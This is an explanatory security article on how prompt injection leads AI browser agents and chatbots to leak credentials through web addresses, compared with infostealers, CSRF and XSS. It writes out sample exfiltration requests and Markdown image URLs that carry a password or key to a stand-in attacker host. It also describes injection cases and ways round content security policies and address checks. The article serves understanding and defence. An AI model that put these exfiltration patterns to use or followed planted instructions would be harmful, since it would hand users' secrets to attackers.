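# How AI browser agents can leak credentials through ordinary web requests

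## What a logged-in session and a web address each carry

A browser agent is an AI model that reads web pages and clicks, types and opens addresses for a user. An AI browser is a browser with such an agent, either built in, as in Perplexity's Comet and OpenAI's ChatGPT Atlas, or added as an extension, such as Anthropic's Claude for Chrome. People use these agents to summarise pages, sort email, compare prices and fill in forms, often in a browser where they are signed in to their email, bank and employer's systems.

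This arrangement lets an attacker steal credentials without malware or a stolen login. The attacker puts text into a page or message that the agent will read. The model treats the text as an instruction from its user, finds a credential (anything that grants access, such as a password or a one-time code) and opens a web address that contains it. The attacker runs the server at that address and so receives the credential. Security researchers call this exfiltration, the movement of data to someone who is not allowed to have it. The browser works as designed throughout, and web standards older than the agents explain most of how the theft happens.

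### Signing in and the session cookie

HTTP, the protocol that browsers and web servers use, treats each request for a page as a separate event. A server that has just checked a password therefore has no built-in way to connect that check with the next request. Cookies provide that connection, and *HTTP State Management Mechanism* (Barth, 2011) describes how they work.

To log in, the user sends a name and password, and perhaps a one-time code from a phone. The server checks them and replies with a session cookie. The cookie contains a session identifier, usually a long random string. In Barth's example, the identifier is named SID and has the value 31d4d96e407aad42. The browser stores the cookie and returns it with every later request to the same site. The server looks up which account the identifier belongs to and sends back that account's page. The logged-in session lasts as long as the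 site accepts the cookie in place of the password and any one-time code. Barth suggests two weeks as a reasonable lifetime for the cookie.

The server therefore recognises the browser rather than the person using it. Whether the user or an agent in that browser clicks on the inbox, the browser sends the same request with the same cookie. A site can look for indirect signs of automation, such as clicks too fast for a human, but the cookie check gives the same result. Barth calls this property ambient authority, meaning that the browser supplies the user's permission automatically, whoever chose the address.

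*Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* (Roesner and Kohlbrenner, 2026) reports tests of seven AI browsers in January and February 2026, some using pages whose content depended on who was visiting. Every agent answered from the user's own version of the page, though ChatGPT Atlas in its agent mode did so only after the user had switched on a logged-in setting, which then stayed on. The tests could not show whether the agents read the page already on the screen or loaded it again with the user's cookies, but either way the agent gets the same content as the signed-in user.

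### What the agent uses and what it can see

The agent depends on the session cookie but usually cannot see it. The cookie travels in a request's headers, which are lines of technical information that pages do not display. Sites can also mark a cookie HttpOnly. *Cookies* (van Kesteren and Hofmann, 2026), a draft revision of the standard, defines this mark as an instruction to the browser to send the cookie to the site as usual but withhold it from scripts running in the page. The browser returns a cookie only to the site that set it, so a request to an attacker's server does not carry the bank's cookie. But a site may omit the HttpOnly mark, and Claude for Chrome could run its own scripts inside pages when Roesner and Kohlbrenner tested it. Such a script could read an unmarked cookie.

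Much else that grants access sits in plain view, because sites print it on pages for people to read and copy:

- A mailbox shows one-time codes and links for resetting passwords.
- A developer's dashboard shows API keys, the strings that programs present to a service in place of a password.
- An account's security settings may show recovery codes, which let the owner back in after losing a phone.
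- A password manager can show everything at once, and in the 1Password case of late 2025 and early 2026 a browser agent read a vault and sent out its contents.

Page text has no equivalent of HttpOnly, so an agent that reads a page can read any secret the page shows to the signed-in user. The dots in a password field don't always hide the text from an agent either. Roesner and Kohlbrenner typed text into such a field and asked each agent what it contained, and both ChatGPT Atlas in agent mode and Claude for Chrome gave the answer. The dots change only how the browser displays the field, and the characters remain in the page's underlying structure, where software can read them.

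The session cookie lets the agent open the page, and the agent then leaks text from the page rather than the cookie itself. This helps the attacker, because a stolen password or API key works from any computer and keeps working after the user's session ends. A one-time code is less useful because it expires within minutes, so the attacker has to be ready to use it.

### What a web address delivers

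The format of web addresses comes from Berners-Lee et al. (2005), in *Uniform Resource Identifier (URI)*. Take an imaginary user whose email address is ana@mail.example and whose password is `blue&tin#7`. The ending ".example" is reserved for documentation, so nobody can register a site under it. An address that carries both values to an equally imaginary server looks like this:

`https://notes.example/save?email=ana%40mail.example&pw=blue%26tin%237`

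| Part | In the example | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | Names the protocol |
| Authority | `notes.example` | Names the server (the host), with a port number if needed |
| Path | `/save` | Names a resource on that server |
| Query string | `email=ana%40mail.example&pw=blue%26tin%237` | Passes values to the server |
| Fragment | none here | Follows a "#" and marks a place within the page; the browser does not send it |

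The address contains percent signs because some characters have special meanings there. An "&" separates one value in the query string from the next, and a "#" begins the fragment. If the address contained the password as Ana types it, the server would read "blue" as the whole password and the browser would never send the "7". Percent-encoding avoids this by replacing a character with a percent sign and its two-digit hexadecimal code, so "&" becomes `%26`, "#" becomes `%23`, and a space becomes `%20`. The standard allows an unencoded "@" in a query string, but most software encodes it anyway, as `%40`. The server reverses the substitution to recover the original text. The process is public and needs no key. Search boxes do the same thing with every query that contains a space.

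When the browser opens the address, it connects to notes.example and sends a request that begins, in slightly simplified form, like this:

```
GET /save?email=ana%40mail.example&pw=blue%26tin%237
Host: notes.example
```

The server now has Ana's email address and password, whether it then responds with a page, an error message or nothing at all. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that websites commonly record the addresses visitors request, so the server's owner can read the values in that log later without needing a program to catch them. The user may never notice, because a browser sends the same kind of request to load an embedded image or preview a link, without opening a page on the screen.

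HTTPS doesn't hide a secret in a web address from the server that receives it. It encrypts the whole address in transit, including the query string, which keeps out eavesdroppers, but the server has to decrypt the request to answer it. Miessler (2015), in *Never Send Sensitive Information in the URL, Even Over HTTPS*, gave this as a reason for site builders to keep secrets out of addresses, and added that browsers store addresses and often pass them to other sites in the "referer" header. Berners-Lee et al. had already advised against an older habit of putting a user name and password before the host name. Both warnings concern secrets leaked through carelessness to whoever happens to see a log, whereas a browser agent under an attacker's influence sends the secret directly to the log's owner.

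### What browsers forbid between sites

A browser with several tabs open holds pages from parties that have no reason to trust one another. The same-origin policy stops a page from one origin from reading the content of a page from another. *The Web Origin Concept* (Barth, 2011) defines an origin as the combination of scheme, host and port. Two pages under `https://example.com` share an origin. `http://example.com` is a different origin because its scheme differs, and `https://www.example.com` is different because its host does. In an example from Roesner and Kohlbrenner, a user has bank.com open in one tab and attacker.com in the next. The attacker's page cannot read or change the bank's page, or access the bank's cookies.

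Barth writes that browsers generally forbid a page to read information from another origin but permit it to send information there. A page may show an image from any site, link to it or submit a form to it, and in each case the browser makes a request to an address that the page's author wrote. According to *Same-Origin Policy*, a wiki page of the W3C, the web's main standards body, pages can make GET requests, which fetch something, and POST requests, which submit something, to other origins, but not the PUT and DELETE requests that some services use to change data. An address with a query string needs only a GET request.

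Browsers allow requests between origins by design. Barth observes that a browser that blocked them would stop its users from following hyperlinks, and the W3C page likewise notes that each site could then link only to itself.

This arrangement works fairly well for ordinary pages because a page can send only what it can read. The script on attacker.com can send anything it has to its own server, but it has no bank data. The bank's page has that data, and its code comes from the bank. In Barth's example of a login form, the page's author specifies the address that will receive the password, and so entrusts the password to whoever controls that address.

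A browser agent breaks this separation because it can read the bank's page on the user's behalf and also open attacker.com. The same-origin policy does not prevent this, because it restricts only the code inside pages. Users can still copy text from one tab to another, and the agent has much the same freedom. Roesner and Kohlbrenner found that some AI browsers also give their agents the content of other origins embedded within a page.

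### The agent's loop and prompt injection

A browser agent works in a loop that starts when the user gives it a task. Software around the model collects the current page as text, underlying code, a screenshot or some mixture of these, and passes it to the model along with the task and a record of earlier steps. The model produces the next action, such as clicking a button, typing text or opening an address. The browser carries out the action with the user's cookies attached, a new page loads, and the software collects that page too. The loop ends when the model produces an answer instead of an action.

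Products differ in how much of this they allow. In Roesner and Kohlbrenner's tests, Firefox's AI mode gave the model a page's text only when the user pressed a button to summarise it, and the model could not act on the page. ChatGPT Atlas in agent mode and Claude for Chrome read pages, clicked and typed much as a person would. All the agents also read text outside the visible part of the page, and Atlas and Claude for Chrome read elements that the page's code had hidden from the user.

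Browser agents are vulnerable because the model receives the developer's instructions, the user's request and the text of the page as one sequence of tokens, the small units of text that a language model processes. Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that models are useful because they follow instructions, but they cannot reliably rank those instructions by where they came from. Prompt injection is text in a page, email or invitation that a model treats as an instruction from its user.

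Willison coined the term "prompt injection" by analogy with SQL injection, an older attack in which text that a visitor types into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can reliably prevent SQL injection by passing the command and the visitor's text to the database separately, but language models have no equally reliable way to separate instructions from the text they are given to process. Willison also distinguishes prompt injection from jailbreaking, in which someone tries to get a model to produce content its developer has forbidden. A jailbreak may embarrass the developer, while prompt injection usually harms the user, who has asked for nothing improper.

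Willison's "lethal trifecta" is a set of three conditions that together let an attacker steal data through an AI system: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. Many systems meet all three only after someone connects several tools to them. A browser agent in a logged-in session meets them from the start, because the pages behind the sign-in are private, almost anyone can write a web page or send an email, and opening an address sends data. Removing any one condition stops the theft. In a later collection of notes, *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, Willison calls sending data out by far the easiest condition to restrict without making a system much less useful. Restricting it is harder for a browser agent, which has to open web addresses to do its work.

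### From planted text to an opened address

The leak takes three steps, and each gets past safeguards that were built for something else.

1. **The agent reads planted text.** The user asks for a summary of a page or an inbox, and the attacker's instruction is somewhere in it. The attacker needed no login to put it there, only a web page or an email account. A malware scanner finds no program to block, because there is only prose. What remains is the model's own tendency to ignore such text. In June 2025 Willison thought there was a "very good chance" that a model would obey it. Developers have since worked on that tendency, but it remains a tendency, and Roesner and Kohlbrenner argue that it cannot give the guarantees that a rule in the browser's own design can.

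2. **The agent reads a secret.** It opens the mailbox, dashboard or vault, the browser attaches the session cookie, and the site returns the page. The checks on the password and the one-time code took place at sign-in, perhaps days ago. HttpOnly protects the cookie, but the secret is in the text. The same-origin policy still keeps the attacker's page out of the mailbox, and the attacker's page never tries to get in. A site that asks for the password again before it shows recovery codes can stop the leak here, as can a locked vault, so long as the agent has no way to supply the password itself.

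3. **The agent opens an address.** It writes the secret into a query string, and the browser sends the request. The same-origin policy permits requests to other sites. HTTPS encrypts this one all the way to the attacker's server, which decrypts it like any other visitor's, and the secret is in the log before the page has finished loading.

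## Before browser agents: theft by malware and by forged requests

Attackers stole passwords and session cookies from browsers long before browsers had agents, and malware is still a common way to do it. Other attacks need no malware because they trick a program that already has a user's permission into using that permission for the attacker. An agent leak gives an attacker the same kind of data as malware does, but it works by tricking the agent in this way, so most malware defences miss it.

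### How an infostealer works

An infostealer is malware that copies saved passwords and session cookies from an infected computer and sends them to a criminal's server. Microsoft's *StealC and Amadey* (2026) describes in detail StealC, one of the most widespread infostealers. Criminals who rent StealC get a tool that builds copies of the malware and a web panel for managing the data those copies steal.

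Infostealers usually infect a computer because the user runs a program, not because of a software flaw. Attackers use advertisements and manipulated search results to get people looking for free utilities, cracked applications or game cheats to download a working program with the stealer bundled in. In ClickFix, a fast-growing variant, a website persuades visitors to paste a command into a Windows dialog box, and the command runs the attacker's script. Phishing emails and other malware also deliver infostealers. For example, Amadey, which is also for rent, infects a computer first and then downloads StealC or whatever else its operator chooses.

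Once running, StealC contacts its operator's server and receives a list of what to look for. It then reads the browser's files. Chrome, Edge and similar browsers keep saved passwords, cookies, card details and browsing history in the user's profile folder, which a program the user has started can normally open. The browser encrypts the most sensitive items, so StealC inserts code into another process and decrypts them there. It then searches email, file-transfer and messaging programs and cryptocurrency wallets, and it can take a screenshot of the desktop.

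StealC sends the results to the server in a series of encrypted web requests and can then delete itself. Criminals call the data from one computer a log. Logs often go on sale within hours on criminal markets or Telegram, typically for $10 to $50. Those with bank or company accounts can cost over $100, and one analysis that Microsoft cites found logs for as little as $2. Brokers buy logs in bulk, test which accounts still work and resell the access, often to ransomware groups. A buyer can type a stolen password into the login page, or skip that page by loading a stolen session cookie into another browser, which the site then accepts as the user's. Some break-ins at companies happen within 48 to 72 hours of the theft, while other stolen credentials go unused for months.

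The trade is very large. Flashpoint's *Global Threat Intelligence Report* (2026) counts 7.4 million infected devices and 1.7 billion stolen credentials in the first half of 2026, with infections up 27% on the previous period. Flashpoint sells this kind of intelligence and gathers much of it from the places where criminals trade logs. The *StealC Historical Bot Infection Special Report* (2026), from the non-profit security organisation Shadowserver, covers only one infostealer but uses data from nearer the source, supplied by Dutch police. It counts 384,781 devices and about 9.9 million different logins between July 2025 and June 2026. One infection tends to expose many accounts, and Recorded Future's *2025 Identity Threat Landscape Report* gives an average of 87 stolen credentials per device.

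Police and companies sometimes shut down the servers, but the trade has so far survived. In June 2026 they acted against StealC and Amadey, which Microsoft's *Scaling cybercrime disruption through innovation and AI* (2026) links to more than 140,000 infected computers in the first two weeks of May. In 2025, Microsoft found another infostealer, Lumma, on more than 394,000 Windows computers in two months. It then seized or blocked about 2,300 of Lumma's domains, according to its *Disrupting Lumma Stealer*. Flashpoint still ranks Lumma and its clones among the three most prolific families in 2026.

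### The confused deputy

An infostealer takes credentials so that someone else can impersonate the user from another computer. An attacker can also cause a program that already has the user's authority to misuse it, without taking the credentials. Security engineers call such a program a confused deputy, after Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988), a "nearly true story" about Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers.

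Tymshare's customers could run a compiler, a program that translates source code into machine code, and choose a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also kept statistics in a file in a system directory, so the operating system let it write anywhere in that directory. The directory also held the company's billing records. One customer named the billing file as the destination for debugging output. The operating system allowed this because the compiler had permission to write there, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

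Hardy traces the fault to the compiler, which had authority from both the customer and the company but no way to specify which to use for a given file. Filtering file names would not have helped much. The directory held other sensitive files, the company could add more at any time, and a customer might have a legitimate reason to direct output there. Each new permission or restriction either opened holes in secure programs or broke working ones. By Hardy's last count, the test for opening a file contained fourteen logical operators.

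Hardy proposed replacing file names with capabilities, which are references that both identify a file and carry permission to use it. The company would give the compiler a capability for the statistics file, and the customer would supply one for the debugging output. A customer with no capability for the billing file could not supply that file as the debugging output.

A browser agent resembles Hardy's compiler. It has the user's authority over every account the user is signed in to, and it follows instructions from the user and, when a prompt injection works, from text written by a stranger. The agent is harder to repair, though, because its next action comes from a model that has just read a page. A programmer could search the compiler's code for every line that opened a file, but no line of code corresponds to the agent's decision to open the mailbox.

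### Forged requests and injected scripts

On the web, the browser can be the confused deputy. In cross-site request forgery, as MDN's *Cross-site request forgery (CSRF)* defines it, an attacker gets a user's browser to send a request to a site where the user is signed in, and the site carries out a harmful action as if the user had intended it. Suppose Ana, from the example above, is signed in to a shop and opens an attacker's page in another tab. A script on the page submits a hidden form that changes the delivery address on her shop account. The browser attaches the shop's session cookie, so the shop makes the change. SameSite Wiki's *Cross-Site Request Forgery (CSRF)* calls this a confused-deputy flaw and attributes it to ambient authority, the automatic use of cookies that Barth described.

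Copes points out in *Protect cookie requests from CSRF* that the attacker never sees the shop's response. The same-origin policy stops the attacker's page from reading it. Request forgery can therefore change data but not read it, whereas an agent leak depends on reading data.

Sites have good defences against forgery. A site can put a random token in each of its own forms and reject submissions without it, since an attacker's page cannot read the token. It can also mark its cookies SameSite, which makes the browser leave them out of most requests that start on other sites. Willison's *Exploring the SameSite cookie attribute for preventing CSRF* dates the first work on this mark to 2016 and notes that all modern browsers support it, although SameSite Wiki lists variants of the attack that get past it. Neither defence stops a browser agent, because the agent uses the site's own pages and buttons,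 as Ana would, so each request starts on the site itself and carries the right token and cookie. The request that sends the secret to the attacker's server needs no cookie from Ana's account.

Unlike request forgery, cross-site scripting lets an attacker read data from the site. It happens when a site copies one visitor's text into a page that another visitor will load, without converting the characters that have special meaning in the page's code. If the text contains a script, the second visitor's browser runs it as part of the site. Because the script has the site's origin, it can read the page and any cookie not marked HttpOnly, and send what it finds to the attacker in a query string. MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025) ranks cross-site scripting first and request forgery third.

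Cross-site scripting is the older attack most similar to an agent leak, but a careful site can prevent it by converting special characters so that the browser displays the attacker's text instead of running it. This conversion doesn't stop text planted for an agent, because the model reads the displayed words. A site with no flaw in its code can therefore deliver a prompt injection. An agent can also read planted text on one site and a secret on another, whereas an injected script can read only from the origin where it runs.

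### One account under both attacks

Suppose Ana rents servers from cloud.example. Her browser stores her account password and session cookie. The account's dashboard displays an API key, which her programs use to control the servers. The table shows the steps of two attacks on this account, one by an infostealer and one through her browser agent.

| Stage | Infostealer | Browser agent |
|---|---|---|
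| Entry | Ana downloads a free video converter with the stealer bundled in | Ana asks the agent to summarise her inbox, where one email contains planted text |
| Code run on the machine | The attacker's program | Only the AI browser that Ana installed |
| Privilege used | Ana's Windows account, which can open her browser's files | Ana's logged-in session at cloud.example |
| How the secret is read | The malware decrypts the saved password and the session cookie | The agent opens the dashboard and reads the API key as page text |
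| How it leaves | Encrypted uploads to the operator's server | A web address with the key in its query string, opened in the browser |
| What the attacker holds afterwards | The password and cookie for cloud.example, and usually those for many other sites | The API key, and anything else the agent read and sent |
| Traces left | Signs of tampering with the browser's data, connections to a criminal server, and later a sign-in from an unfamiliar computer | The planted email, possibly an entry in the browser's history, and any record the product keeps of the agent's steps |

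An infostealer takes more secrets in a single run. Planted text has to lead the agent to each secret in turn, although a password vault holds many of them in one place. The secrets the agent takes can stay valid longer, since an API key usually still works after the session ends, and changing the account password may not revoke it.

The clean-up differs as well. After an infection, Ana should assume that everything in the browser has been stolen. She has to remove the malware, change her passwords and end her sessions, because stolen cookies keep working after the malware is gone, as Google's *Fighting cookie theft using device bound sessions* warns. After an agent leak, she may have only a few secrets to replace, but she may not know that anything leaked. In the 1Password case documented in Zenity Labs' *PerplexedBrowser*, the agent reported back to the user as if the task had gone normally.

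Criminals infect millions of computers a year with infostealers, while the 1Password case was a demonstration by researchers. Malware is probably the larger risk for most people today, so a defence can be well worth having even if it doesn't stop agents from leaking credentials.

### Antivirus and cookie protection

Antivirus software looks for known malicious files and for suspicious behaviour, such as one program inserting code into another. It can detect an infostealer by either sign, but it can miss a new build, and many infections happen on home computers that no company monitors. In an agent leak, the only program involved is the browser, which is opening pages as usual, so there is no malicious file or suspicious behaviour of this kind to detect.

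Encrypting stored cookies has made them harder for infostealers to steal. Chrome on Windows formerly relied on a system service that protected cookies from other users of the computer but not from malicious programs running under the same user's account. *Improving security of Chrome cookies* (Google, 2024) describes app-bound encryption, which Google added in July 2024. A service with system privileges writes the application's identity into the encrypted data and will not decrypt it for a different application. Malware now has to gain system privileges or insert code into Chrome, and antivirus software is more likely to detect either. Chrome also records an event in the Windows log when an identity check fails. Google presented the change as a way to make theft harder, and StealC's developers have evidently done the extra work, since the malware inserts code into another process to defeat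 this protection. Encryption makes no difference to an agent, because the browser itself decrypts the cookies to use them.

*Protecting Cookies with Device Bound Session Credentials* (Ackerman, Rubery and Ehinger, 2026) concludes that on any operating system, software alone cannot reliably stop malware from copying cookies. Device Bound Session Credentials (DBSC) makes the copies much less useful. When a session begins, the browser creates a pair of cryptographic keys, using a security chip if the computer has one. It sends the public key to the site and keeps the private key on the computer. The site then issues cookies that expire quickly, and the browser must prove that it holds the private key to get new ones. A thief who moves a cookie to another computer can use it until it expires but cannot renew it.

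Chrome 146 brought DBSC to Windows in April 2026. In May, Google made it the default for Google accounts in Chrome on Windows, according to its *Prevent account takeovers with Device Bound Session Credentials (DBSC)* (2026). Ackerman and colleagues report a significant reduction in session theft where DBSC was in use, but give no figure. Other sites have to add support on their own servers, where mistakes can go unnoticed. Helme's *Everything I learned shipping Device Bound Session Credentials* describes two faults that turned bound sessions back into ordinary ones while everything seemed to work. Browser support is also incomplete. Delitz's *Device Bound Session Credentials (DBSC) explained* (2025), last revised in October 2026, lists support in Chrome and Edge but no announced plans for Safari.

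Device binding does not help against an agent leak, because Ana's API key is not a cookie and the agent runs on her own computer, where the browser renews the cookies whenever they expire. W3C's draft standard, *Device Bound Session Credentials* (2025), explicitly does not aim to prevent a similar case, in which an attacker present on the device uses the session temporarily. Planted text gives an attacker much the same access for as long as the agent follows it, without any malware on the device to detect.

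### Multi-factor sign-in and passkeys

Multi-factor sign-in requires a second proof besides the password, such as a one-time code. It can stop a thief who has only the password, but not one who has the session cookie, because the site issues the cookie after the user passes both checks. In 2025, Recorded Future indexed 276 million credentials with active session cookies, which was 31% of the credentials it indexed from malware.

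A browser agent also starts work after both checks, so if it leaks a credential, the second factor can only limit what the attacker does next. A leaked password is not enough at a site that also requires a code, unless the agent can read the code too, for instance in Ana's mailbox. An API key usually works without a code. According to Zenity Labs, a second factor in the 1Password case would have stopped the attacker from logging in to the captured account but not from receiving passwords from the vault.

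A passkey replaces the password with a key pair. The site stores the public key, and the user's device proves at sign-in that it has the private key, normally after the user confirms with a fingerprint, face scan or PIN. Unless the site keeps a password as a fallback, there is no password for the browser to save or for an agent to read off a page, which removes one secret that both attacks target.

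Passkeys protect the sign-in but not the session that follows it. According to W3C, WebAuthn, the web standard behind passkeys, provides secure sign-in, and DBSC protects users afterwards. An infostealer can copy the cookie a site issues after a passkey sign-in just as it can copy any other. The agent also starts after Ana has signed in, so the dashboard shows it the same API key whether she used a passkey or a password.

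### What the network shows

Ana's internet provider, her employer and whoever runs the Wi-Fi in a café can watch the traffic between her computer and the web. What they learn depends on whether they can decrypt it.

When the agent opens a URL at `notes.example`, the browser first looks up the server's numerical address, often without encryption. It then starts an encrypted connection with an opening message that usually names the host in readable form, so that a server with several sites can present the right certificate. An outside observer can therefore see `notes.example`, the numerical address, the time and roughly how much data passes, but not the path, the query string or the page that comes back. Newer protocols can also hide the lookup and the host name in the opening message, which leaves the observer with little more than the numerical address. A request with Ana's API key in the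 query string looks to the observer like any other short visit to the same host.

Many companies send their employees' traffic through an inspecting proxy, which can read the full address of each encrypted request, including the query string. The company installs its own certificate on each work computer so that the browser trusts the proxy to stand in for other sites. The browser encrypts its request to the proxy, which decrypts and examines it, then opens a second encrypted connection to the real site. The proxy can also record the request or block it.

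A proxy could catch some agent leaks this way. Many services give their API keys a recognisable prefix or length that a filter can search for. A password or a six-digit code has no such pattern, and ordinary addresses are full of long, meaningless strings from search forms and advertising trackers. The request also may not show whether Ana or the agent chose the address. An inspecting proxy can read the secret and may detect it, so Zenity Labs goes too far in calling the leak indistinguishable from routine browsing at the network layer, though that is a fair description of what an outside observer sees. A proxy that records full addresses also keeps a copy of the secret, which is the problem Miessler raised about secrets in web addresses. Companies can instead limit which addresses the agent may open, whatever they contain.

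Network monitoring works better against infostealers than against theft through browser agents. StealC encrypts stolen data before sending it, so even a proxy may be unable to read it, but the destination can reveal the theft. The same servers collect data from many victims, and once researchers have identified a server, companies can block it and search their records for earlier connections. Microsoft and its partners identified more than 200 such domains and IP addresses for StealC and Amadey. An attacker who uses an agent needs only an ordinary web server, which may never have been used in an attack before.

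Account records can also expose malware theft when they show a stolen cookie or password being used on an unfamiliar computer. In Google Workspace, Google's suite for organisations, administrators can view binding events for device-bound sessions in the audit logs. An agent leak leaves little evidence of this kind. While the agent reads the dashboard, cloud.example records Ana's usual browser, her usual network and a valid session. The first unusual entry appears when the attacker uses the API key from somewhere else, and even that may look normal on a service whose customers run programs in many places.

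### Extensions that steer an agent

Some attacks put malicious code on the computer and then also use an agent's authority. The code is usually a browser extension, a small program that the user adds to the browser. An extension can also steal without an agent. LayerX's *How We Discovered A Campaign of 16 Malicious Extensions* describes at least 16 extensions from one developer that claimed to improve ChatGPT but were built to steal users' ChatGPT accounts.

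BragJack, an attack that Forever Security disclosed in September 2026, exploits the browser's AI features. The Hacker News' *One Extension Could Hijack AI Assistants* (2026) reports that the researchers made it work on Gemini Live in Chrome, Comet, Microsoft Edge, Opera Neon and Claude for Chrome. In each product, a model on the company's servers directs a browser component that can see the screen or take actions. The component accepts commands only from one trusted web page, such as perplexity.ai for Comet. Extensions aren't allowed to command the component, but they can be allowed to change web pages, so the researchers' extension inserted code into the trusted page and sent its commands from there. The extension needed two common permissions, one to alter pages, which ad blockers also use, and one to alter the browser's network traffic.

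Trent (2026), in *Security Check-in Quick Hits*, distinguishes this technique, "Prompt Forcing", from classic prompt injection because the extension gives the agent all of its instructions instead of hiding text in something the agent reads. Training a model to ignore instructions in web pages would probably not help, because the extension's instructions arrive through the channel that normally carries the user's.

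In Comet, Edge, Opera Neon and Claude for Chrome, the extension could control the agent. Trent mentions a demonstration in which an agent summarised a user's emails and sent them out. The researchers considered Comet the worst case because the extension could also read any file on the computer. In Chrome, the extension could read files on the computer, take screenshots and switch on the camera and microphone, but it could not control an agent. Google fixed the Chrome flaw in January 2026, and Microsoft fixed the one in Edge in July. The other three findings come only from Forever Security's own account, though it lists a reward for each.

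These were demonstrations, and all of them required the malicious extension to already be running in the victim's browser. An extension that has permission to alter a page can generally read it too, so it often does not need an agent to copy an email. BragJack mainly gave extensions powers they do not normally have, such as reading local files or operating the camera.

According to CyberScoop, LayerX found a bug in Anthropic's Chrome extension that let any other extension, even one with no special permissions, plant hidden instructions for Claude. An extension that could not open Ana's mailbox might then get the agent to open it, much as Tymshare's customer reached the billing file through the compiler. In such cases, defenders at least have a program to look for. A company can forbid extensions it has not approved, and removing the malicious one cuts off its access to the agent, whereas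 instructions hidden in an email can arrive again in the next one.

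## 2023 to mid-2025: chatbots leak data through image and link addresses

AI products leaked data through web addresses before they could operate a browser. Most chatbots in early 2023 could not click or type on a website, but they could include an image's address in a reply, and the user's browser opened that address to display the reply.

### The image leak

Chatbots usually format their replies in Markdown, a simple notation in which, for example, two asterisks on either side of a word make it bold. This line inserts a picture:

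`![Sales chart](https://images.example/chart.png)`

The chat page turns the line into an ordinary web image, and the browser requests the file from images.example. The user does not need to click anything, because browsers load the images on a page automatically.

Suppose Ana pastes an API key into a chat to ask about an error, and later asks the chatbot to summarise a web page that contains instructions planted by an attacker. The model follows them and includes an image in its reply. The image's address points to notes.example, the attacker's server, and contains the key in its query string. When Ana's browser requests the image, it sends the key to the attacker. Ana sees a small or broken picture. The model only writes text and the browser makes the request, so even a chatbot that can't open web pages can leak anything in its input.

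Security researcher Johann Rehberger demonstrated this on Bing Chat, a Microsoft chatbot that could read the user's open page, and described it in *Bing Chat*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red. The planted text was of a kind that any commenter or advertiser could put on a page. Bing Chat began to follow the text right away, but the image appeared only after two more turns of conversation. The image's address contained a short summary of the page and the chat, along with a secret from further down the same page.

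Roman Samoilenko described a similar leak from ChatGPT in the same month, April 2023. *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (Willison, 2023) explains that a website adds instructions to any text a visitor copies from it, and the visitor unknowingly pastes them into the chat. The data then leaks through the address of a single-pixel image. Many other products had the same flaw, including Google Bard, Writer, Amazon Q and Google NotebookLM (Willison, *GitHub Copilot Chat*).

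### Microsoft's fix and content security policy

Rehberger reported the Bing Chat leak to Microsoft on 8 April 2023 and the ChatGPT leak to OpenAI the next day. Microsoft fixed the Bing Chat leak within about two months. Rehberger's original post records a notice of the fix on 15 June, but a later post, Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, dates the fix to May.

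From the outside, Microsoft's fix appeared to rely on content security policy, a browser feature that predates chatbots. A site can send a policy along with each of its pages, and the browser then enforces it while the page is open. The policy consists of directives, each of which covers one kind of request. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, defines `img-src` as the directive for images. A chat page could arrive with this policy:

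`Content-Security-Policy: img-src https://images.example`

The browser would load the sales chart above but refuse to request an image from notes.example. It checks the address before sending the request, so the key in the query string never leaves Ana's computer, whether or not the model recognised the planted text. Rehberger found that Bing Chat's policy allowed images from only four addresses, all belonging to Bing.

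The protection such a policy gives depends on what its list allows. W3C warns that a site can block every other kind of request and still leak data if it allows images from anywhere. W3C also advises setting `default-src`, a fallback directive, because some requests have no directive of their own, such as prefetches, which load something early in case the user wants it.

Even a short list of allowed sites can include one that passes data on. Janc (2018), a Google engineer, wrote on a W3C mailing list that preventing exfiltration was not really a goal of the standard, because most developers allowed so many sites that an attacker could often get data out through one of them. For instance, an attacker might send the data to an analytics service on the list and collect it there.

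Two later cases support Janc's point. Willison, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, describes how Salesforce's policy for its Agentforce product still listed an expired domain. Researchers from Noma Security registered the domain in 2025 and received data about sales leads in image requests. In January 2026, the email product Superhuman allowed images from docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms. A Google Form can store values sent in a web address, so an attacker could send a victim's emails to their own form and read them there.

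### OpenAI's first address check

OpenAI at first said that displaying images from Markdown was a feature and that it planned no changes, according to Rehberger's *ChatGPT Plugins*. Anthropic fixed the same leak in Claude that year, as Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* records, while ChatGPT remained vulnerable to it.

OpenAI introduced its first defence in December 2023, a day after Rehberger used the leak in a live demonstration. ChatGPT's web page began sending each image address to an OpenAI server and displayed the image only if the server classified the address as safe. Because OpenAI used this check instead of sending the browser a fixed list of allowed sites, ChatGPT could show images from many more sites than Bing Chat could. OpenAI did not publish the rule for classifying addresses.

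Rehberger soon found a gap in the check, as Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes. The attacker sets up 36 images, one for each letter and digit, and the model displays them in the order that spells the secret. No single address contains the secret or looks suspicious. Nine of Rehberger's 36 addresses passed the check, which was enough to send the word "hi" as two requests.

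The method is slow, but a one-time code has only six digits. In a later post, Rehberger points out two obstacles: requests can arrive out of order, and a browser may reuse an image it has just loaded instead of requesting it again. A code of 447744 might then produce only two requests, one for each different digit. The attacker would know which digits the code contains, but not their order or how many times each appears.

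The check also ran only in the web version of ChatGPT, so the iOS app still loaded the images. Rehberger presented more ways around it at the Black Hat Europe conference in 2024. The security company Tenable (2025) reported another bypass to OpenAI in December 2024 and published it before OpenAI had deployed a fix. A stronger version of the check, which Rehberger dates to around August 2025, stopped the conference attacks. In January 2026, OpenAI said that it now compares addresses with an index of pages already public on the web.

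### Links and link previews

A chatbot can put data in the address of a link instead of an image, but then the user normally has to click the link. *Trust No AI* (2024) describes a case from February 2024 in which a phishing email caused Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office software, to search the user's inbox and write what it found into a link. The link encoded the data in characters that the screen does not display, so the user could not see it. Microsoft fixed the flaw in July 2024. Amazon dealt with a similar flaw in Amazon Q for Business by no longer turning addresses into links.

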